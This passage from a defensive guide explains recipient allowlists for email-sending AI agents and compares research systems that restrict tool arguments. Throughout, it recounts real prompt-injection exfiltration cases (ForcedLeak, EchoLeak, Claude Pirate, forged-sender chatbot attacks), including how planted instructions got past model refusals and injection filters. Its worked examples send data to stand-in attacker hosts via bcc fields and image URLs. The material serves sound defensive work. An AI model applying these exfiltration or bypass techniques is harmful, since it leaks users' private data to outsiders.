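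A rule that an agent may answer only the person who wrote to it does not help when that person is the attacker. SC Media's *Sloppy AI defenses take cybersecurity back to the 1990s, researchers say* describes a demonstration in which a researcher, Sharbat, persuaded a customer-service agent to email him customer records, which such a rule would have permitted. The agent was modelled on one used by the consulting firm McKinsey. *Pwn the Enterprise*, the researchers' own notes, reports that the injection no longer works and that they received an $8,000 bounty for it.

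### One domain per session

Some agents need to email a company they have never contacted, but no one else. Mint Security's *Designing safe production AI agents via tool scoping* describes an agent that asks software vendors about their privacy practices. The first email in an investigation sets the permitted domain, which usually comes from the vendor's known website. Later emails must go to that domain, and the agent accepts replies only from it. The run also ends after each email, so the agent can't send several in a row.

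Binding a session to one domain confines a hijacked session to one outside company. An agent that has already read a malicious web page could choose the attacker's domain, so the application should take the domain from the user's request or a supplier record. The rule also causes false refusals when a vendor's privacy team writes from its parent company's domain.

Mint Security's sample code puts the policy check in a hook that runs after the mail tool, so the email has already been sent by the time the check rejects a recipient. Putting the same check in a hook that runs before the tool would stop the email from being sent.

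### Whole domains

A rule that permits example.com lets the office assistant write to every colleague without anyone maintaining a list of names. AWS's *Identity and access management in Amazon SES* shows how Amazon's mail service can apply such a rule to the To, Cc and Bcc recipients. The comparison in its example is case-sensitive, so the service would refuse dana@EXAMPLE.COM unless the application first converted the domain to lower case.

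The rule blocks mail to any domain the attacker has just registered, but it allows mail to every address at example.com, including the wrong Dana's. To find such mistakes, Nylas advises running the agent for at least 14 days in a mode that logs the intended recipients and sends nothing, then reviewing the log by hand. This is a good way to find the entries a new list needs, but two weeks of ordinary mail may not include an attack.

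Shared and expired domains cause further problems, described in "How allowlists have failed". For most office assistants, a sensible compromise is to allow every address at the company's own domain but only specific addresses outside it.

### A check for send_email

The pseudocode below follows that compromise. `parse_plain` stands for the parsing part of the `approved_recipient` function given earlier, and `refuse` ends the whole call.

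```
function check_send_email(call, user, lists):

    for each field in [to, cc, bcc]:
        for each raw in call[field]:
            address = parse_plain(raw)          # refuse if ambiguous
            if address not in lists.addresses
               and domain(address) not in lists.domains:
                refuse(field, "recipient not permitted")
            replace raw with address in call[field]

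    if call has a reply_to field:
        refuse("reply_to", "field not available")
    call.reply_to = user.address                # code fills this in

    if call.body would load images or other remote content:
        refuse("body", "remote content not permitted")
    for each link in call.body:
        if host(link) not in lists.link_hosts:
            refuse("body", "link not permitted")

    return call                                 # send this version
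```

The reply-to address is easy to forget because the original message isn't sent there. Nylas' sample check covers only `to`, `cc` and `bcc`, and AWS documents no condition for reply-to addresses. But the field can divert Dana's answer, and it can also leak data. *Hacking AI customer service agents* (Ayoub and De Ceukelaire, 2026) describes how hidden text in an email made Chrome's built-in assistant write a case number into an attacker's reply-to address. Chrome's vulnerability programme marked the report "Won't Fix".

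The body needs a check because a mail program may contact other servers when Dana opens the message. The model can write a secret into the web address of an image at attacker.test, and Dana's mail program will send it to the attacker when it loads the image. A tool that escapes HTML, as recommended earlier, can't include images, so this check matters mainly for tools that allow formatted messages. An ordinary link usually leaks nothing until someone clicks it, but some security scanners open links automatically. Mail programs also turn bare names such as attacker.test/page into links, so the code that looks for links must find those too.

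For the office assistant, `lists.domains` contains example.com, and `lists.addresses` contains one client, sam@partner.example. The call from the running example produces this result:

```
to         dana@example.com          domain permitted     pass
cc         none                                           pass
bcc        stranger@attacker.test    on neither list      REFUSE
reply_to   not checked, because the call has ended
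body       not checked, because the call has ended
```

Nobody receives the notes, including Dana. If the model then proposes the same email without the blind copy, the email passes and Dana gets her notes. If the stranger asks for an image at attacker.test instead, all the recipients pass, but the check on the body blocks the call.

The link rule will cause some false refusals, since meeting notes often cite outside websites. The application can show those links to the user instead of refusing them. The check will also allow an email to accounts@example.com that the user never asked for. Preventing this requires an allowlist computed for each task.

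### Chatbots that email a transcript

Letting the person talking to an agent supply the email address is risky, as customer-service chatbots show. Heaton (2026) notes in *Your chatbot can email people on your behalf* that many of them let visitors enter an email address to receive a copy of the conversation. Inti De Ceukelaire, a founding member of the bug-bounty company Intigriti, examined such chatbots for a talk at the 2026 DEF CON security conference. His research on customer-service agents earned more than $50,000 in bounties over a few weekends.

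A transcript contains whatever the visitor typed or got the chatbot to write. A visitor who enters someone else's address can therefore make the company's own mail system send that person a phishing message. One of the chatbots also continued conversations by email. De Ceukelaire emailed it with the victim's address forged as the sender, then used a simple prompt to make it send the victim a phishing email from the support address.

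Some chatbots could also look up account details or take actions for a customer. In these cases, De Ceukelaire forged an email from the victim and put his own address in the Cc field. The chatbot copied him into its reply, which contained the victim's data.

Abuse of typed addresses doesn't require AI. KrebsOnSecurity (2025) reports that its author received thousands of emails in a few hours from companies that use Zendesk. Anyone could open a support ticket at these companies under another person's address, and that person then received an automatic confirmation with a subject line the abuser had chosen. The article concludes that the abuse would have been impossible if the companies had validated the addresses before replying. Malwarebytes' *Spammers abuse Zendesk to flood inboxes with legitimate-looking emails, but why?* (2026) reports that the abuse was still going on in January 2026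 and that some people complained of more than 1,000 emails.

A domain allowlist can't solve this, because a company's customers may have addresses anywhere. The recipient should instead come from an authenticated record. The transcript tool then has no address parameter, and the application reads the address from the account of the customer who has logged in:

```
recipient = logged_in_customer.verified_email
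```

Visitors without an account can download the transcript. If the company wants to email it to them, it should first send a code to the address they gave and wait for them to enter the code. That first message also goes to an address a stranger typed, so it should have fixed text and a strict limit on how often the system sends it.

An email's sender field is a poor substitute for a login, even when the mail server authenticates senders. De Ceukelaire wrote an email with two sender addresses, his own and a victim's. The server authenticated his address, but the agent looked up the victim's account, and the reply with the victim's data went to him. To prevent this, the application has to establish one identity and use it for both the account lookup and the reply. Changing an account's email address should also require confirmation from the old address. Otherwise, an attacker could ask the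 agent to change the address before requesting the data.

### Agents that write to strangers

Nylas says that a fixed allowlist doesn't suit a sales tool that emails any prospect. It suggests dropping the domain check and relying more on human approval, detection of unusual recipients, and a limit on volume, such as 50 emails an hour and 200 a day. The volume limit helps against spam and runaway loops but does little to prevent exfiltration, because an attacker may need only one email to get the data out.

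Many sales agents can still use an allowlist. If staff choose the prospects and import their addresses, the agent can write to thousands of strangers without being able to add recipients itself. This prevents the agent from finding new prospects and contacting them unaided, but the company could let it propose them in batches for an employee to approve, preferably with the source of each address.

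A support agent also has to answer whoever writes in, but it needs more than published information. Once the application has authenticated a customer, the agent's tools should return only that customer's orders and messages. An attacker who hijacks the conversation will then receive only their own data. The agent in Sharbat's demonstration could reach other customers' records, and checking the recipient could not have made that safe.

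### Who may add an entry

An entry for a whole domain gives the agent access to everyone there, so an administrator should approve it. Users can reasonably add single addresses for their own assistants, on a settings page that the agent can't operate. The agent must not be able to edit the list, even indirectly through something such as a contacts tool that writes to the address book the check reads. Otherwise, the stranger's email could ask the agent to add the address before sending to it. Considus keeps its exceptions in a configuration file that the assistant can't reach.

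Each entry should record who requested it, why, and when it expires:

```
address     sam@partner.example
reason      office renovation contract
requested   user 0388, approved by IT on 2026-11-02
expires     2027-03-31
```

An expiry date is more reliable than a plan to tidy the list, because when a forgotten entry expires, someone will notice the refusal. AWS's mail service can enforce these dates, since its policies can limit sending to a given period. Permanent entries, such as the company's own domain, need a review date and a named owner. The review should cover the agents as well as their lists, because Microsoft warns that agents nobody has used for weeks, and agents whose owners have left, can keep running with old permissions.

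### What happens after a refusal

The refusal message goes back to the model, which may be following the attacker's instructions. It should therefore name the field and the reason without offering alternatives:

```
Email not sent. The bcc field contains a recipient that
company policy does not permit. Do not try another address.
Tell the user.
```

Cloudflare returns a specific error code when a recipient isn't on the list, so an application can distinguish this refusal from a temporary fault worth retrying. An error message listing the permitted addresses would help an agent correct a typo, but it would also show a hijacked agent where it could still send mail. The application should also notify the user directly, because a hijacked agent may not pass the message on.

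Some refused calls should go to a person. If the user typed a new client's address into the request, the application can ask for confirmation and then send the email. If the address appeared only in something the agent had read, the user may still have wanted it, as when a colleague's email gives the client's address. The application should show where the address came from and ask more pointedly whether to send the email. It should treat a blind copy that nobody requested as a possible attack, like a blocklisted domain, and should stop the task and alert the security staff. The application should not ask about every refusal, although that would be simpler, because users who see many such questions tend to approve them without reading.

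Approval also depends on what the person sees. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe emails with one version of the text for human readers and another for the agent, so the employee who checks the agent's work may never see the planted instruction. In another attack, an email quoted a fake earlier message from the support team. The support software displayed the quoted message as a genuine approval, and the agent issued a $4,200 refund.

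The confirmation screen should show the arguments of the call, including every recipient in full, not the model's summary of them. The application should record the user's decision itself and never look for it in the email thread. Approval should cover only that message. Adding the new address to the allowlist should be a separate choice with its own expiry date.

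## How allowlists have failed

To get past an allowlist, an attacker has to receive the data through a domain already on the list. Researchers have done this to several well-known products. Most of their demonstrations involve web addresses, because many assistants that can't send email still display their answers in a browser. An image in such an answer can leak data through its web address, just as one in an email can. Websites limit this with a Content Security Policy, an allowlist of the domains a page may load images and other content from. Allowlists of email recipients can have the same faults.

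### A permitted domain that had expired

Salesforce's Agentforce lets companies build agents that work with their customer records. In July 2025, the security company Noma found that a stranger could make such an agent leak those records. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) is a repost of Noma's full report on a security forum. The Hacker News (2025) reports the flaw's severity as 9.4 out of 10.

The attack began with Web-to-Lead, a form on a company's website that adds visitors who fill it in to the company's records as possible customers. Noma planted instructions in an entry. When an employee asked the agent to deal with that entry, the agent also looked up the email addresses of other possible customers and put them in the web address of an image.

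The form allowed 40 characters for a first name or company and 80 for a last name or email address, which Noma judged too short for its instructions. The description field allowed 42,000. A limit of 1,000 would not have stopped the attack, because Noma's text was about 400 characters long. A limit low enough to block that text would also have blocked many genuine enquiries.

Salesforce's Content Security Policy should have stopped the browser from loading the image. It allowed 22 domains, but the registration of one of them, my-salesforce-cms.com, had expired. Noma bought the domain for $5 and received the email addresses there. The entry was presumably correct when Salesforce added it, and it became dangerous without any change to the list.

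Salesforce regained control of the domain (SecurityWeek, *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft*) and audited and corrected its policy (Willison, *ForcedLeak*). On 8 September 2025, it began to enforce a second allowlist, called Trusted URLs, on what its agents produce (Martin, 2025, *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed*). Each customer's administrators had to add the outside domains their agents needed (TechNadu, *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*). Domains on those lists can also expire.

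A program can check for this by looking up each domain through RDAP, the public service for registration records. If the registration date is later than the date of the list entry, someone has re-registered the domain since the company approved it. This test misses a domain that its owner sold without letting it lapse, so the program should also compare the registrar and name servers with those recorded at approval. Exact email addresses need the same check, because anyone who buys partner.example can receive mail for sam@partner.example.

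### Wildcards over a hosting provider's subdomains

MITRE's *CWE-183* covers allowlists that are too permissive because they include an unsafe input that the developers assumed to be safe. One example is the wildcard `*.cloudfront.net`, which permits every subdomain of Amazon's CloudFront service. CloudFront's customers get their own subdomains, so an attacker can get a permitted subdomain by becoming a customer.

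Writer.com, an AI writing service for businesses, had this entry in its policy in 2023. Willison recounts how Kai Greshake and the security firm PromptArmor hid instructions in a web page. When a user asked for a summary of it, the assistant put text from the user's private documents into the address of an image on CloudFront. Writer replied on 5 December that it did not consider this a security issue, but by 18 December the leak appeared to be fixed. A month earlier, researchers had found a similar fault in Google's assistant, Bard, whose policy allowed images only from Google's own subdomains. One of those, script.google.com, runs programs that anyone can write.

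Many websites have entries like Writer's. SensePost's *Dress Code* reports that in 2023, 1,441 of the top million sites permitted `*.cloudfront.net` and 860 permitted `*.amazonaws.com`, and it classes both as usable for exfiltration. Salesforce's list also included `*.amazonaws.com` in 2025, so an attacker might not have needed the expired domain, and regaining it would not have been enough to fix the problem.

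To check whether a wildcard is safe, an administrator has to find out who can get a name under it. The Public Suffix List, which browsers use, includes many domains under which the public can get subdomains, such as cloudfront.net. The list is incomplete, so a wildcard can be unsafe even if its domain isn't on it. PromptArmor advises Salesforce customers to add each address explicitly and to avoid wildcards that cover sites with user-generated content. Logs of past requests will usually show which few subdomains an agent needs.

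### A domain that many customers share

Replacing a wildcard with an exact host name doesn't help if the attacker can open an account on that host. Claude can run code in a sandbox, and in 2025 the sandbox's default network setting allowed little more than the sites where programmers download software. Willison noted in September that the list also included api.anthropic.com, which programs use to reach Claude models. Anyone can open an Anthropic account and upload files to it through that address.

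Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how Johann Rehberger exploited this in October. He put instructions and a key to his own Anthropic account in a document. When a user asked Claude to summarise the document, Claude saved the user's last conversation as a file and uploaded it to Rehberger's account. An attacker could take up to 30 megabytes per upload this way. Claude refused many attempts, apparently because the key looked suspicious, until Rehberger disguised the instructions better.

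Rehberger reported the flaw on 25 October, and Anthropic closed the report an hour later as out of scope. On 30 October the company said closing it had been a mistake. Rehberger had proposed that the sandbox let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

The problem came up again in January 2026, two days after Anthropic released Cowork, an agent for general office work. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that Cowork could also upload a user's files to a stranger's account. Anthropic acknowledged the risk and promised to update the virtual machine in which Cowork ran code, according to TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*.

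Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains the eventual fix. A proxy inside the virtual machine intercepts requests to api.anthropic.com and passes only those with the current session's token, so a stranger's key no longer works. Anthropic could not make this check on its servers, because a request from Cowork looks the same there as one from any other program. The proxy also blocks headers that could make the server fetch data from elsewhere. The company now thinks of an allowlist entry as a "capability grant", because the entry permits everything the domain can do.

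It is less clear how well the fix covers Anthropic's products today. Harmonic Security's *Securing Claude Cowork* (2026) reports that since July, Cowork has by default run code on Anthropic's servers instead of the user's computer. According to Anthropic's help page, these cloud sessions can't reach private or internal addresses, but that restriction alone would not stop an upload to a public service. Anthropic describes the proxy for Cowork's virtual machine but doesn't say whether the code tool that Rehberger tested has the same protection. A company that uses either product can test this with two of its own accounts by trying to upload a harmless file from one account's sandbox with the other account's key.

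Form services are shared in the same way. In January 2026, Willison described an attack on the email assistant Superhuman AI, whose policy permitted images from docs.google.com. Google Forms runs on that domain, and a form can record data contained in the web address a browser requests. An email with planted instructions made the assistant send the contents of dozens of other emails to an attacker's form. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw. But Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses docs.google.com as its example of an entry to add.

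For each entry, the auditor should therefore ask whether a member of the public can open an account there and receive data through it. This is possible at any large webmail provider, so a list of recipients should never permit the provider's whole domain.

### A permitted service that forwards data

A permitted host can also pass data on to one that isn't permitted. This happened in EchoLeak, a flaw that the security firm Aim Labs found in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions from their mail and files. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the attack. An attacker sent an employee an email with instructions worded as if for a human reader, which got them past Microsoft's filter for prompt injection. When the employee later asked Copilot about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email and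 put sensitive data into the web address of an image. Copilot normally removed outside links and images from its answers, but it missed those written in one particular way.

The browser would still have refused to load an image from the attacker's domain. Microsoft's policy had 29 different entries, 11 of them wildcards, and 14 appeared twice, which suggests that nobody had reviewed the list for some time. One wildcard covered the subdomains of teams.microsoft.com, where a service fetched any web address it received. The browser sent its request to that service, as the policy allowed, and the service then requested the attacker's address, which contained the data. Aim Labs found a similar service in SharePoint, but the attack worked through that service only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

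According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, before the details became public on 11 June as CVE-2025-32711. Nobody found evidence that criminals had used it. Among other changes, Copilot now removes images and the overlooked kind of link from outside content.

In June 2026, Varonis disclosed another attack on Copilot, SearchLeak, that used Bing's image search to forward the data. Bing's domains were already on the policy that Aim Labs had published a year earlier. The user had to click a link, but it led to a genuine microsoft.com address. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, as The Next Web reports, and has fixed it. Auditing the policy's 29 entries after EchoLeak could have prevented SearchLeak, but only if the auditors had examined what each service under bing.com could do.

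Services that preview links, resize images or translate web pages take a web address as input, and so do pages that redirect visitors. An auditor can give such a service the address of a server the company runs and see whether a request arrives.

Email sent to an address at the company's own domain can still be forwarded to outsiders, and a check on the recipient's address won't detect this. The address projects@example.com may be a mailing list with outside members, or a former employee's mailbox may forward everything to a private account. Administrators can export the mailing lists' members and the forwarding rules, then search both for outside addresses.

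### What to check besides the domain

A domain name identifies a host and not the person who receives the data. If a host serves many customers or forwards requests, the rule has to restrict something else as well:

| Permitted destination | What else the rule should fix |
|---|---|
| Another company's mail domain | the exact mailbox |
| A programming interface with many customers | the credential |
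| A file-storage service | the account or folder that receives the file |
| A form service | the full path of the form |
| A service that fetches web addresses | the addresses it may fetch |

For an agent that files reports with an outside service, the entry might look like this:

```
host         api.example.net
method       POST
path         /v1/reports
credential   the company's own, added by the application
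parameters   no web addresses
```

The agent never needs to see the credential. The application can delete any key the agent put in the request and add the company's own, so the report can only go to the company's account. The application should normalise the path before comparing it, or a path containing `../` could lead elsewhere on the host.

These rules are easy to enforce when the agent calls a tool, because the application builds the request and has the full web address. They are harder to enforce when the agent can run its own code. Web traffic is normally encrypted, so an ordinary proxy can read the host name but not the path or the credential. To check those, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic, as Anthropic's does, which makes the proxy itself sensitive software. Anthropic found that the standard isolation software in its products had held up well, but that its own allowlist proxy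 had failed.

Narrow rules also need more maintenance. If the outside service moves its reports to `/v2/reports`, the application will refuse legitimate calls until somebody updates the entry.

### Auditing an existing list

An allowlist, unlike a blocklist, is usually short enough to audit by hand, as the policies of Salesforce and Copilot were. Removing a bad entry also closes that route permanently, whereas an attacker whose domain is blocklisted can switch to another. But the services behind an entry are harder to count, and their owners can add new ones without notice, so one audit is not enough.

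An allowlist with some bad entries still blocks most destinations. In a test in February 2026, one of Anthropic's researchers tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that told it to send login credentials to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instruction came from the user, Anthropic concluded that only limits on the files and network connections available to the agent could have stopped the transfer.

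An audit of the office assistant's permitted recipients and web hosts might produce these results:

```
example.com            a mailing list has two outside members
                       -> ask the user before sending to that list

sam@partner.example    entry ends 2027-03-31, but the domain's
                       registration ends 2027-01-15
                       -> confirm the renewal or end the entry sooner

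*.hosting.example      anyone can rent a subdomain
                       -> permit only the supplier's own subdomain

forms.example.net      anyone can create a form
                       -> permit only /f/staff-survey

api.example.net        accepts any customer's key
                       -> have the application add the company's key

events.example         no owner on record, unused for eight months
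                       -> remove
```

Entries that no agent has used for months are a good place to start, since the company can usually delete them without studying the services behind them. A program can check domain registrations every day, which is worthwhile because somebody may buy an expired domain as soon as it becomes available. A person has to check for shared accounts and forwarding services, perhaps every few months and whenever a provider announces a new feature on a permitted domain.

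## Setting the permitted recipients for each task

A fixed allowlist permits the same recipients whatever the user asks. It is too wide when the notes should go only to Dana, and too narrow when the user has just typed a new client's address. Ideally, the permitted recipients would depend on the request:

| Request | Who may receive the email | Where the address comes from |
|---|---|---|
| "Send this quote to lee@newclient.example" | Lee | the request |
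| "Send the notes to Dana" | Dana | the company directory or Dana's earlier emails |
| "Answer the client who wrote this morning" | that client | the sender field of the client's email |
| "Send the report to the address in the minutes" | whoever the minutes name | text that other people wrote |

A program can easily check an address that the user typed. It is much harder to check one that the agent looked up in the minutes, because anyone who can edit the minutes can change it, and the user did ask for the report to go to the address given in them. Requests that leave the agent to look up a value are common, at least in benchmarks. *ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) sorted 117 test tasks by how much the request specified. In 47 tasks the request gave every value, and in 56 it named the action but left the agent to look up a value. In the other 14 it left even the action open, as in "do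 what this email asks".

Researchers have built several systems that work out the permitted values from the request, the source of each value, or both. The systems differ mainly in which text they treat as trusted and how much they rely on a language model.

### The AgentDojo benchmark

Most tests of these systems use AgentDojo, as did the Tool-Guard tests. *AgentDojo* (2024) introduced the benchmark with 97 user tasks and 629 security test cases, and the current version has 949. The tasks belong to four suites: Workspace (email, calendar and files), Banking, Travel and Slack. According to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), the benchmark places the attacker's text where outsiders' text would naturally appear, such as in an email body or a file. After each run, ordinary code checks whether an email was sent or money was moved in the simulated environment,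 so the scoring doesn't rely on a language model.

Each security test pairs a user's task with an attacker's goal. Researchers report both the attack success rate and utility, the share of user tasks that the agent completes. Both figures are needed to judge a check, because one that refuses every call would have an attack success rate of zero but be useless.

A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, has 60 harder tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life. Many require the agent to change its plan after reading something.

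### Rules written from the request

Tsai and Bagdasarian built Conseca at Google and describe it in *Contextual Agent Security* (2025). For each request, a language model writes a policy before the agent starts. The model reads the request, the tool documentation and any other context the developer has declared trustworthy. For each tool, the model decides whether the agent may use it, writes a regular expression for each argument, and gives a human-readable reason. Ordinary code then enforces the policy.

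In one example, the user, Alice, asks the agent to answer urgent work emails. The generated policy forbids deleting emails and sets these conditions for sending one (leaving out parts of the patterns that have no effect):

```
sender      contains a match for   alice
recipient   contains a match for   @work\.com
subject     contains a match for   urgent
```

The recipient pattern has no anchor at the end, so it also accepts stranger@work.com.attacker.test. The stated reason is that the recipient must be on the work email list, but the pattern accepts any address at work.com. Tsai and Bagdasarian rely on experts to check that reasons and rules agree. If nobody does, a model can repeat the mistakes programmers make when they write allowlists as text searches.

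Even a correct pattern describes only the form of an address. Ma and colleagues object that it can't separate a legitimate value from an injected one if both match. The model that writes the policy can make it tighter if it has the exact address in advance, so Conseca's prototype treats the addresses in the user's mailbox and the names of files and folders as trusted. But outsiders may have chosen some of these addresses and names. Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge that an address could contain malicious instructions, and an attachment's file name could too. The instructions would then reach the model that writes the policy.

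In a test with 20 office tasks, an agent without any policy completed 14.0 on average, and one with Conseca completed 12.0. An agent under a fixed policy that forbade all changes completed none. The researchers also planted an email with instructions to forward security reports to a colleague at the same company. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except the one in which the user had told the agent to follow the instructions in urgent emails. This result is encouraging because any fixed list of permitted domains would have included the company's own, but the researchers tested only one planted email.

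Conseca's policy can't take account of anything the agent learns during the task. Progent, described by Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, also starts with rules that a model writes from the request, and blocks any call that no rule permits. After some tool results, the model proposes a new policy. A solver, a program that decides logical questions exactly, then compares the sets of calls that the old policy $P$ and the new policy $P'$ permit. If

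$$A(P') \subseteq A(P)$$

the new policy permits nothing that the old one refused, and Progent applies it automatically. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval, from a person or from a setting the developer has chosen.

Suppose the user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. At first the agent may only search for that email. One item on the list is to send a summary on Slack, so the model proposes to permit Slack messages, which is an expansion. Once the agent has found the user's Slack name, the model restricts the recipient to that name, which doesn't require approval. If a planted instruction later leads the model to propose sending the inbox to a stranger, the solver detects another expansion.

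An attacker could exploit narrowing, although Shi and colleagues consider it safe because it only removes permissions. In this example, the approved policy permits Slack messages to anyone until the model narrows it. An injection that arrives before then could make the model narrow the recipient to the attacker, and the solver would accept that because the attacker was already a permitted recipient. An approver should therefore look for destination arguments that an expansion leaves open.

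On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, even with every policy expansion approved automatically. The initial policy alone reduced it to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the policies, the rate fell to zero, and only 6% of updates needed a decision.

Progent can combine a task's rules with a company's permanent ones, but it checks the permanent rules first, and if one of them allows a call, it ignores the task's rules. A permanent rule that allows all mail to example.com would therefore let the agent send an invoice to accounts payable, whatever the user had asked. If the developer instead writes a rule that forbids mail to anyone not on the company's list, the task's rules can narrow the permitted recipients further.

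### A plan fixed before the agent reads anything

CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google DeepMind, separates planning from reading. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its design. A planning model sees only the user's request and writes a short program. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and returns values that the program asks for. For the meeting notes, the program might be:

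```
emails  = search_mail("Dana")
address = quarantined_model("Find Dana's address", emails)
notes   = find_file("notes of Tuesday's meeting")
send_email(to=[address], attachments=[notes])
```

The stranger's request for a blind copy has no effect here, because the program contains no blind copy and nothing the quarantined model reads can add one. But the stranger could write that Dana has a new address, and the quarantined model might return it. CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it, and a policy function checks these records before each tool call. The policy could refuse an address taken from an outsider's email, or refuse to send the notes to anyone who isn't permitted to read them.

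CaMeL treats the request, the system prompts and the outputs of some tools as trusted. If Dana's address appears only in untrusted emails, a policy based on sources will block her correct address as well as a wrong one. Nikolaou and colleagues' extension of CaMeL finds such conflicts before the program runs by checking it against rules, such as one that forbids messages to untrusted recipients. The program above would fail that check immediately, and the planner could try again, perhaps using the company directory.

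The bigger difficulty is that the planner has to foresee every step. Ma and colleagues ran CaMeL with four models on AgentDyn, where tasks often depend on what the agent finds. CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the models.

### Naming the permitted sources

Ma and colleagues' own system, ROPE, lets the agent plan as it goes and restricts where the value of each sensitive argument may come from. It trusts three kinds of text:

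- the request and the user's own identity, such as their email address
- content from a source that the request names and the platform has authenticated, such as an email from a particular sender
- fields of the user's own records that outsiders can't write, such as the product numbers in an order history

Before the task starts, a model called the router reads the request and some trusted account facts, then picks a rule for each sensitive argument from a short list. For example, a rule may require the recipient to appear in the request, to appear in content from a named source, or to equal one particular address. If the router doesn't choose a rule, a default applies. Code then checks every call that changes something. Each item in a list of recipients has to pass, and the value must appear in a trusted text as a whole, not as part of a longer string, so a trusted mention of notevil.com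 doesn't permit evil.com.

In one test, the user asked the agent to summarise a document that Lily had shared by email and send her the summary. Another defence, which planned from the request alone, guessed Lily's address and sent the summary to the wrong address. ROPE's router listed Lily as a source, so ROPE could accept the address in her authenticated email.

When a user wanted an electricity bill paid, however, ROPE refused the payment even though no attacker was involved. The payee's account number appeared only in the bill, which anybody could have written. Ma and colleagues found 96 failed tasks in attack-free runs where ROPE had refused something, and 83 were of this kind. These refusals are hard to avoid because the check would treat a forged account number in the bill the same way.

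On AgentDyn with GPT-4o mini, ROPE reduced attack success from 49.6% to 0.3%. When there was no attack, it completed 36.7% of tasks, compared with 46.7% for the undefended agent. These results depended on a strong router, Claude Opus 4.8. With Gemini 3 Flash as the router, attack success was 5.8%, because the weaker model loosened many of the default rules. When the router could not loosen any default, attack success fell to zero with every model tested, but with the cheaper routers the agent completed only 15.0% to 18.3% of tasks.

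ROPE also depends on the platform to identify correctly who wrote each piece of text. Everything in an email from Lily counts as her text, so if she has forwarded a stranger's message, any address in it presumably becomes acceptable too. A developer could reduce this risk by accepting only the address in the sender field of her email when the task is to reply to her.

### Rules over the flow of data

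Summers, Raghunath and colleagues (2026), in *Environment Steering*, published in September, treat the agent's work as a database. Every tool has one table for its inputs and another for its outputs. A proposed call is a new row in an input table, and a rule can require the row's values to come from particular rows elsewhere. A rule for the meeting notes might look like this:

```
SOURCE REQUIRED DirectoryOutput D
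SINK SendEmailInput E
CONSTRAINT D.name = 'Dana' AND E.recipient = D.email
       AND E.cc IS NULL AND E.bcc IS NULL
ON FAIL RETRY('Use the directory entry for Dana')
```

`SINK` names the table that the rule protects, and `SOURCE` names the table the data must come from. The condition on `cc` and `bcc` is easy to forget, but without it the stranger could still get a blind copy of an email whose main recipient was correct.

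When a call breaks a rule, the system sends the agent a message identifying the failed rule and the tables that hold suitable data. The agent then writes a database query that takes the address from the right table, and the system checks the result again. On AgentDyn with the model Qwen3 235B, this approach completed 61% of tasks and no attack succeeded. The specific message raised task success by 6.5%, while a message that only mentioned a security policy lowered it by 10.5%, and stopping the agent at its first violation lowered it by 36.2%. An office assistant's refusal message could therefore mention the directory without revealing any permitted address.

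The system assumes that the user and whoever writes the rules can be trusted. In the tests, Claude Opus 4.8 wrote most of the rules from a few examples that the researchers had corrected by hand, and Summers and colleagues acknowledge that some rules may be missing or too strict. For this reason, Kimi K2.5, another of the models tested, completed fewer AgentDojo tasks with the rules than without them. In AgentDyn, necessary information and planted instructions also appear in the same document, so the rules cannot require that the information come from a trustworthy source. For those cases, the rules use a language model to check whether the text contains instructions for the agent, so the 0% depends partly on a model that reads the attacker's text.

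### Permitted values enforced while the model writes

In *Only What You've Signed Up For* (October 2026), Cardei, Pinto and colleagues moved the check into text generation. Their system, CoDA, works with diffusion language models, which draft a whole passage at once and revise it over many steps. At each step, CoDA finds the fields that matter for security, such as the recipient in a tool call, and suppresses any tokens that can't form part of a permitted value. It checks complete values, so the model can't combine the start of one permitted name with the end of another.

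The permitted values come from the user's request and sometimes from account records that existed before the task. Cardei and colleagues tested policies that people had refined by hand over several rounds and policies that a language model wrote once from the request. An attacker could rewrite each injection up to 100 times in response to the agent's behaviour. No attack succeeded against the hand-refined policies in any of AgentDojo's four suites, while attacks on the model-written policies succeeded in about 10% of Banking scenarios and in none of the other three suites.

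According to the instructions for the model that writes policies, CoDA can't restrict an argument to values found in files or tool results, and it leaves an argument unrestricted if the request provides no permitted values. The payee field may therefore be unrestricted when a user asks the agent to pay a bill without naming the payee, which may explain the Banking result. When a destination argument has no permitted values, it would be safer to refuse the call or ask the user.

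Constraining the model can also hide an attack that refusing the call could reveal. If only Alice is permitted and planted text makes the model write Eve as the recipient, CoDA changes the recipient to Alice. The message may still be the one the attacker dictated, and nobody sees a refusal. A developer who uses this method should record when the constraint changed a value.

Few developers can change how their model generates text, but many can get a similar effect through strict mode. The application can send a different schema for each task, with an `enum` that lists only that task's permitted recipients, though a person or program still has to produce the list.

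### An index of addresses from typed fields

*SPILLWAY* (Lim, Chang and Lee, November 2026) avoids writing a policy for each task. It relies on the fact that mail tools return an email's sender and body in separate fields. An attacker can write anything in the body, but the mail system fills in the sender. SPILLWAY therefore accepts addresses from fields that hold identities and treats addresses in prose as suspect.

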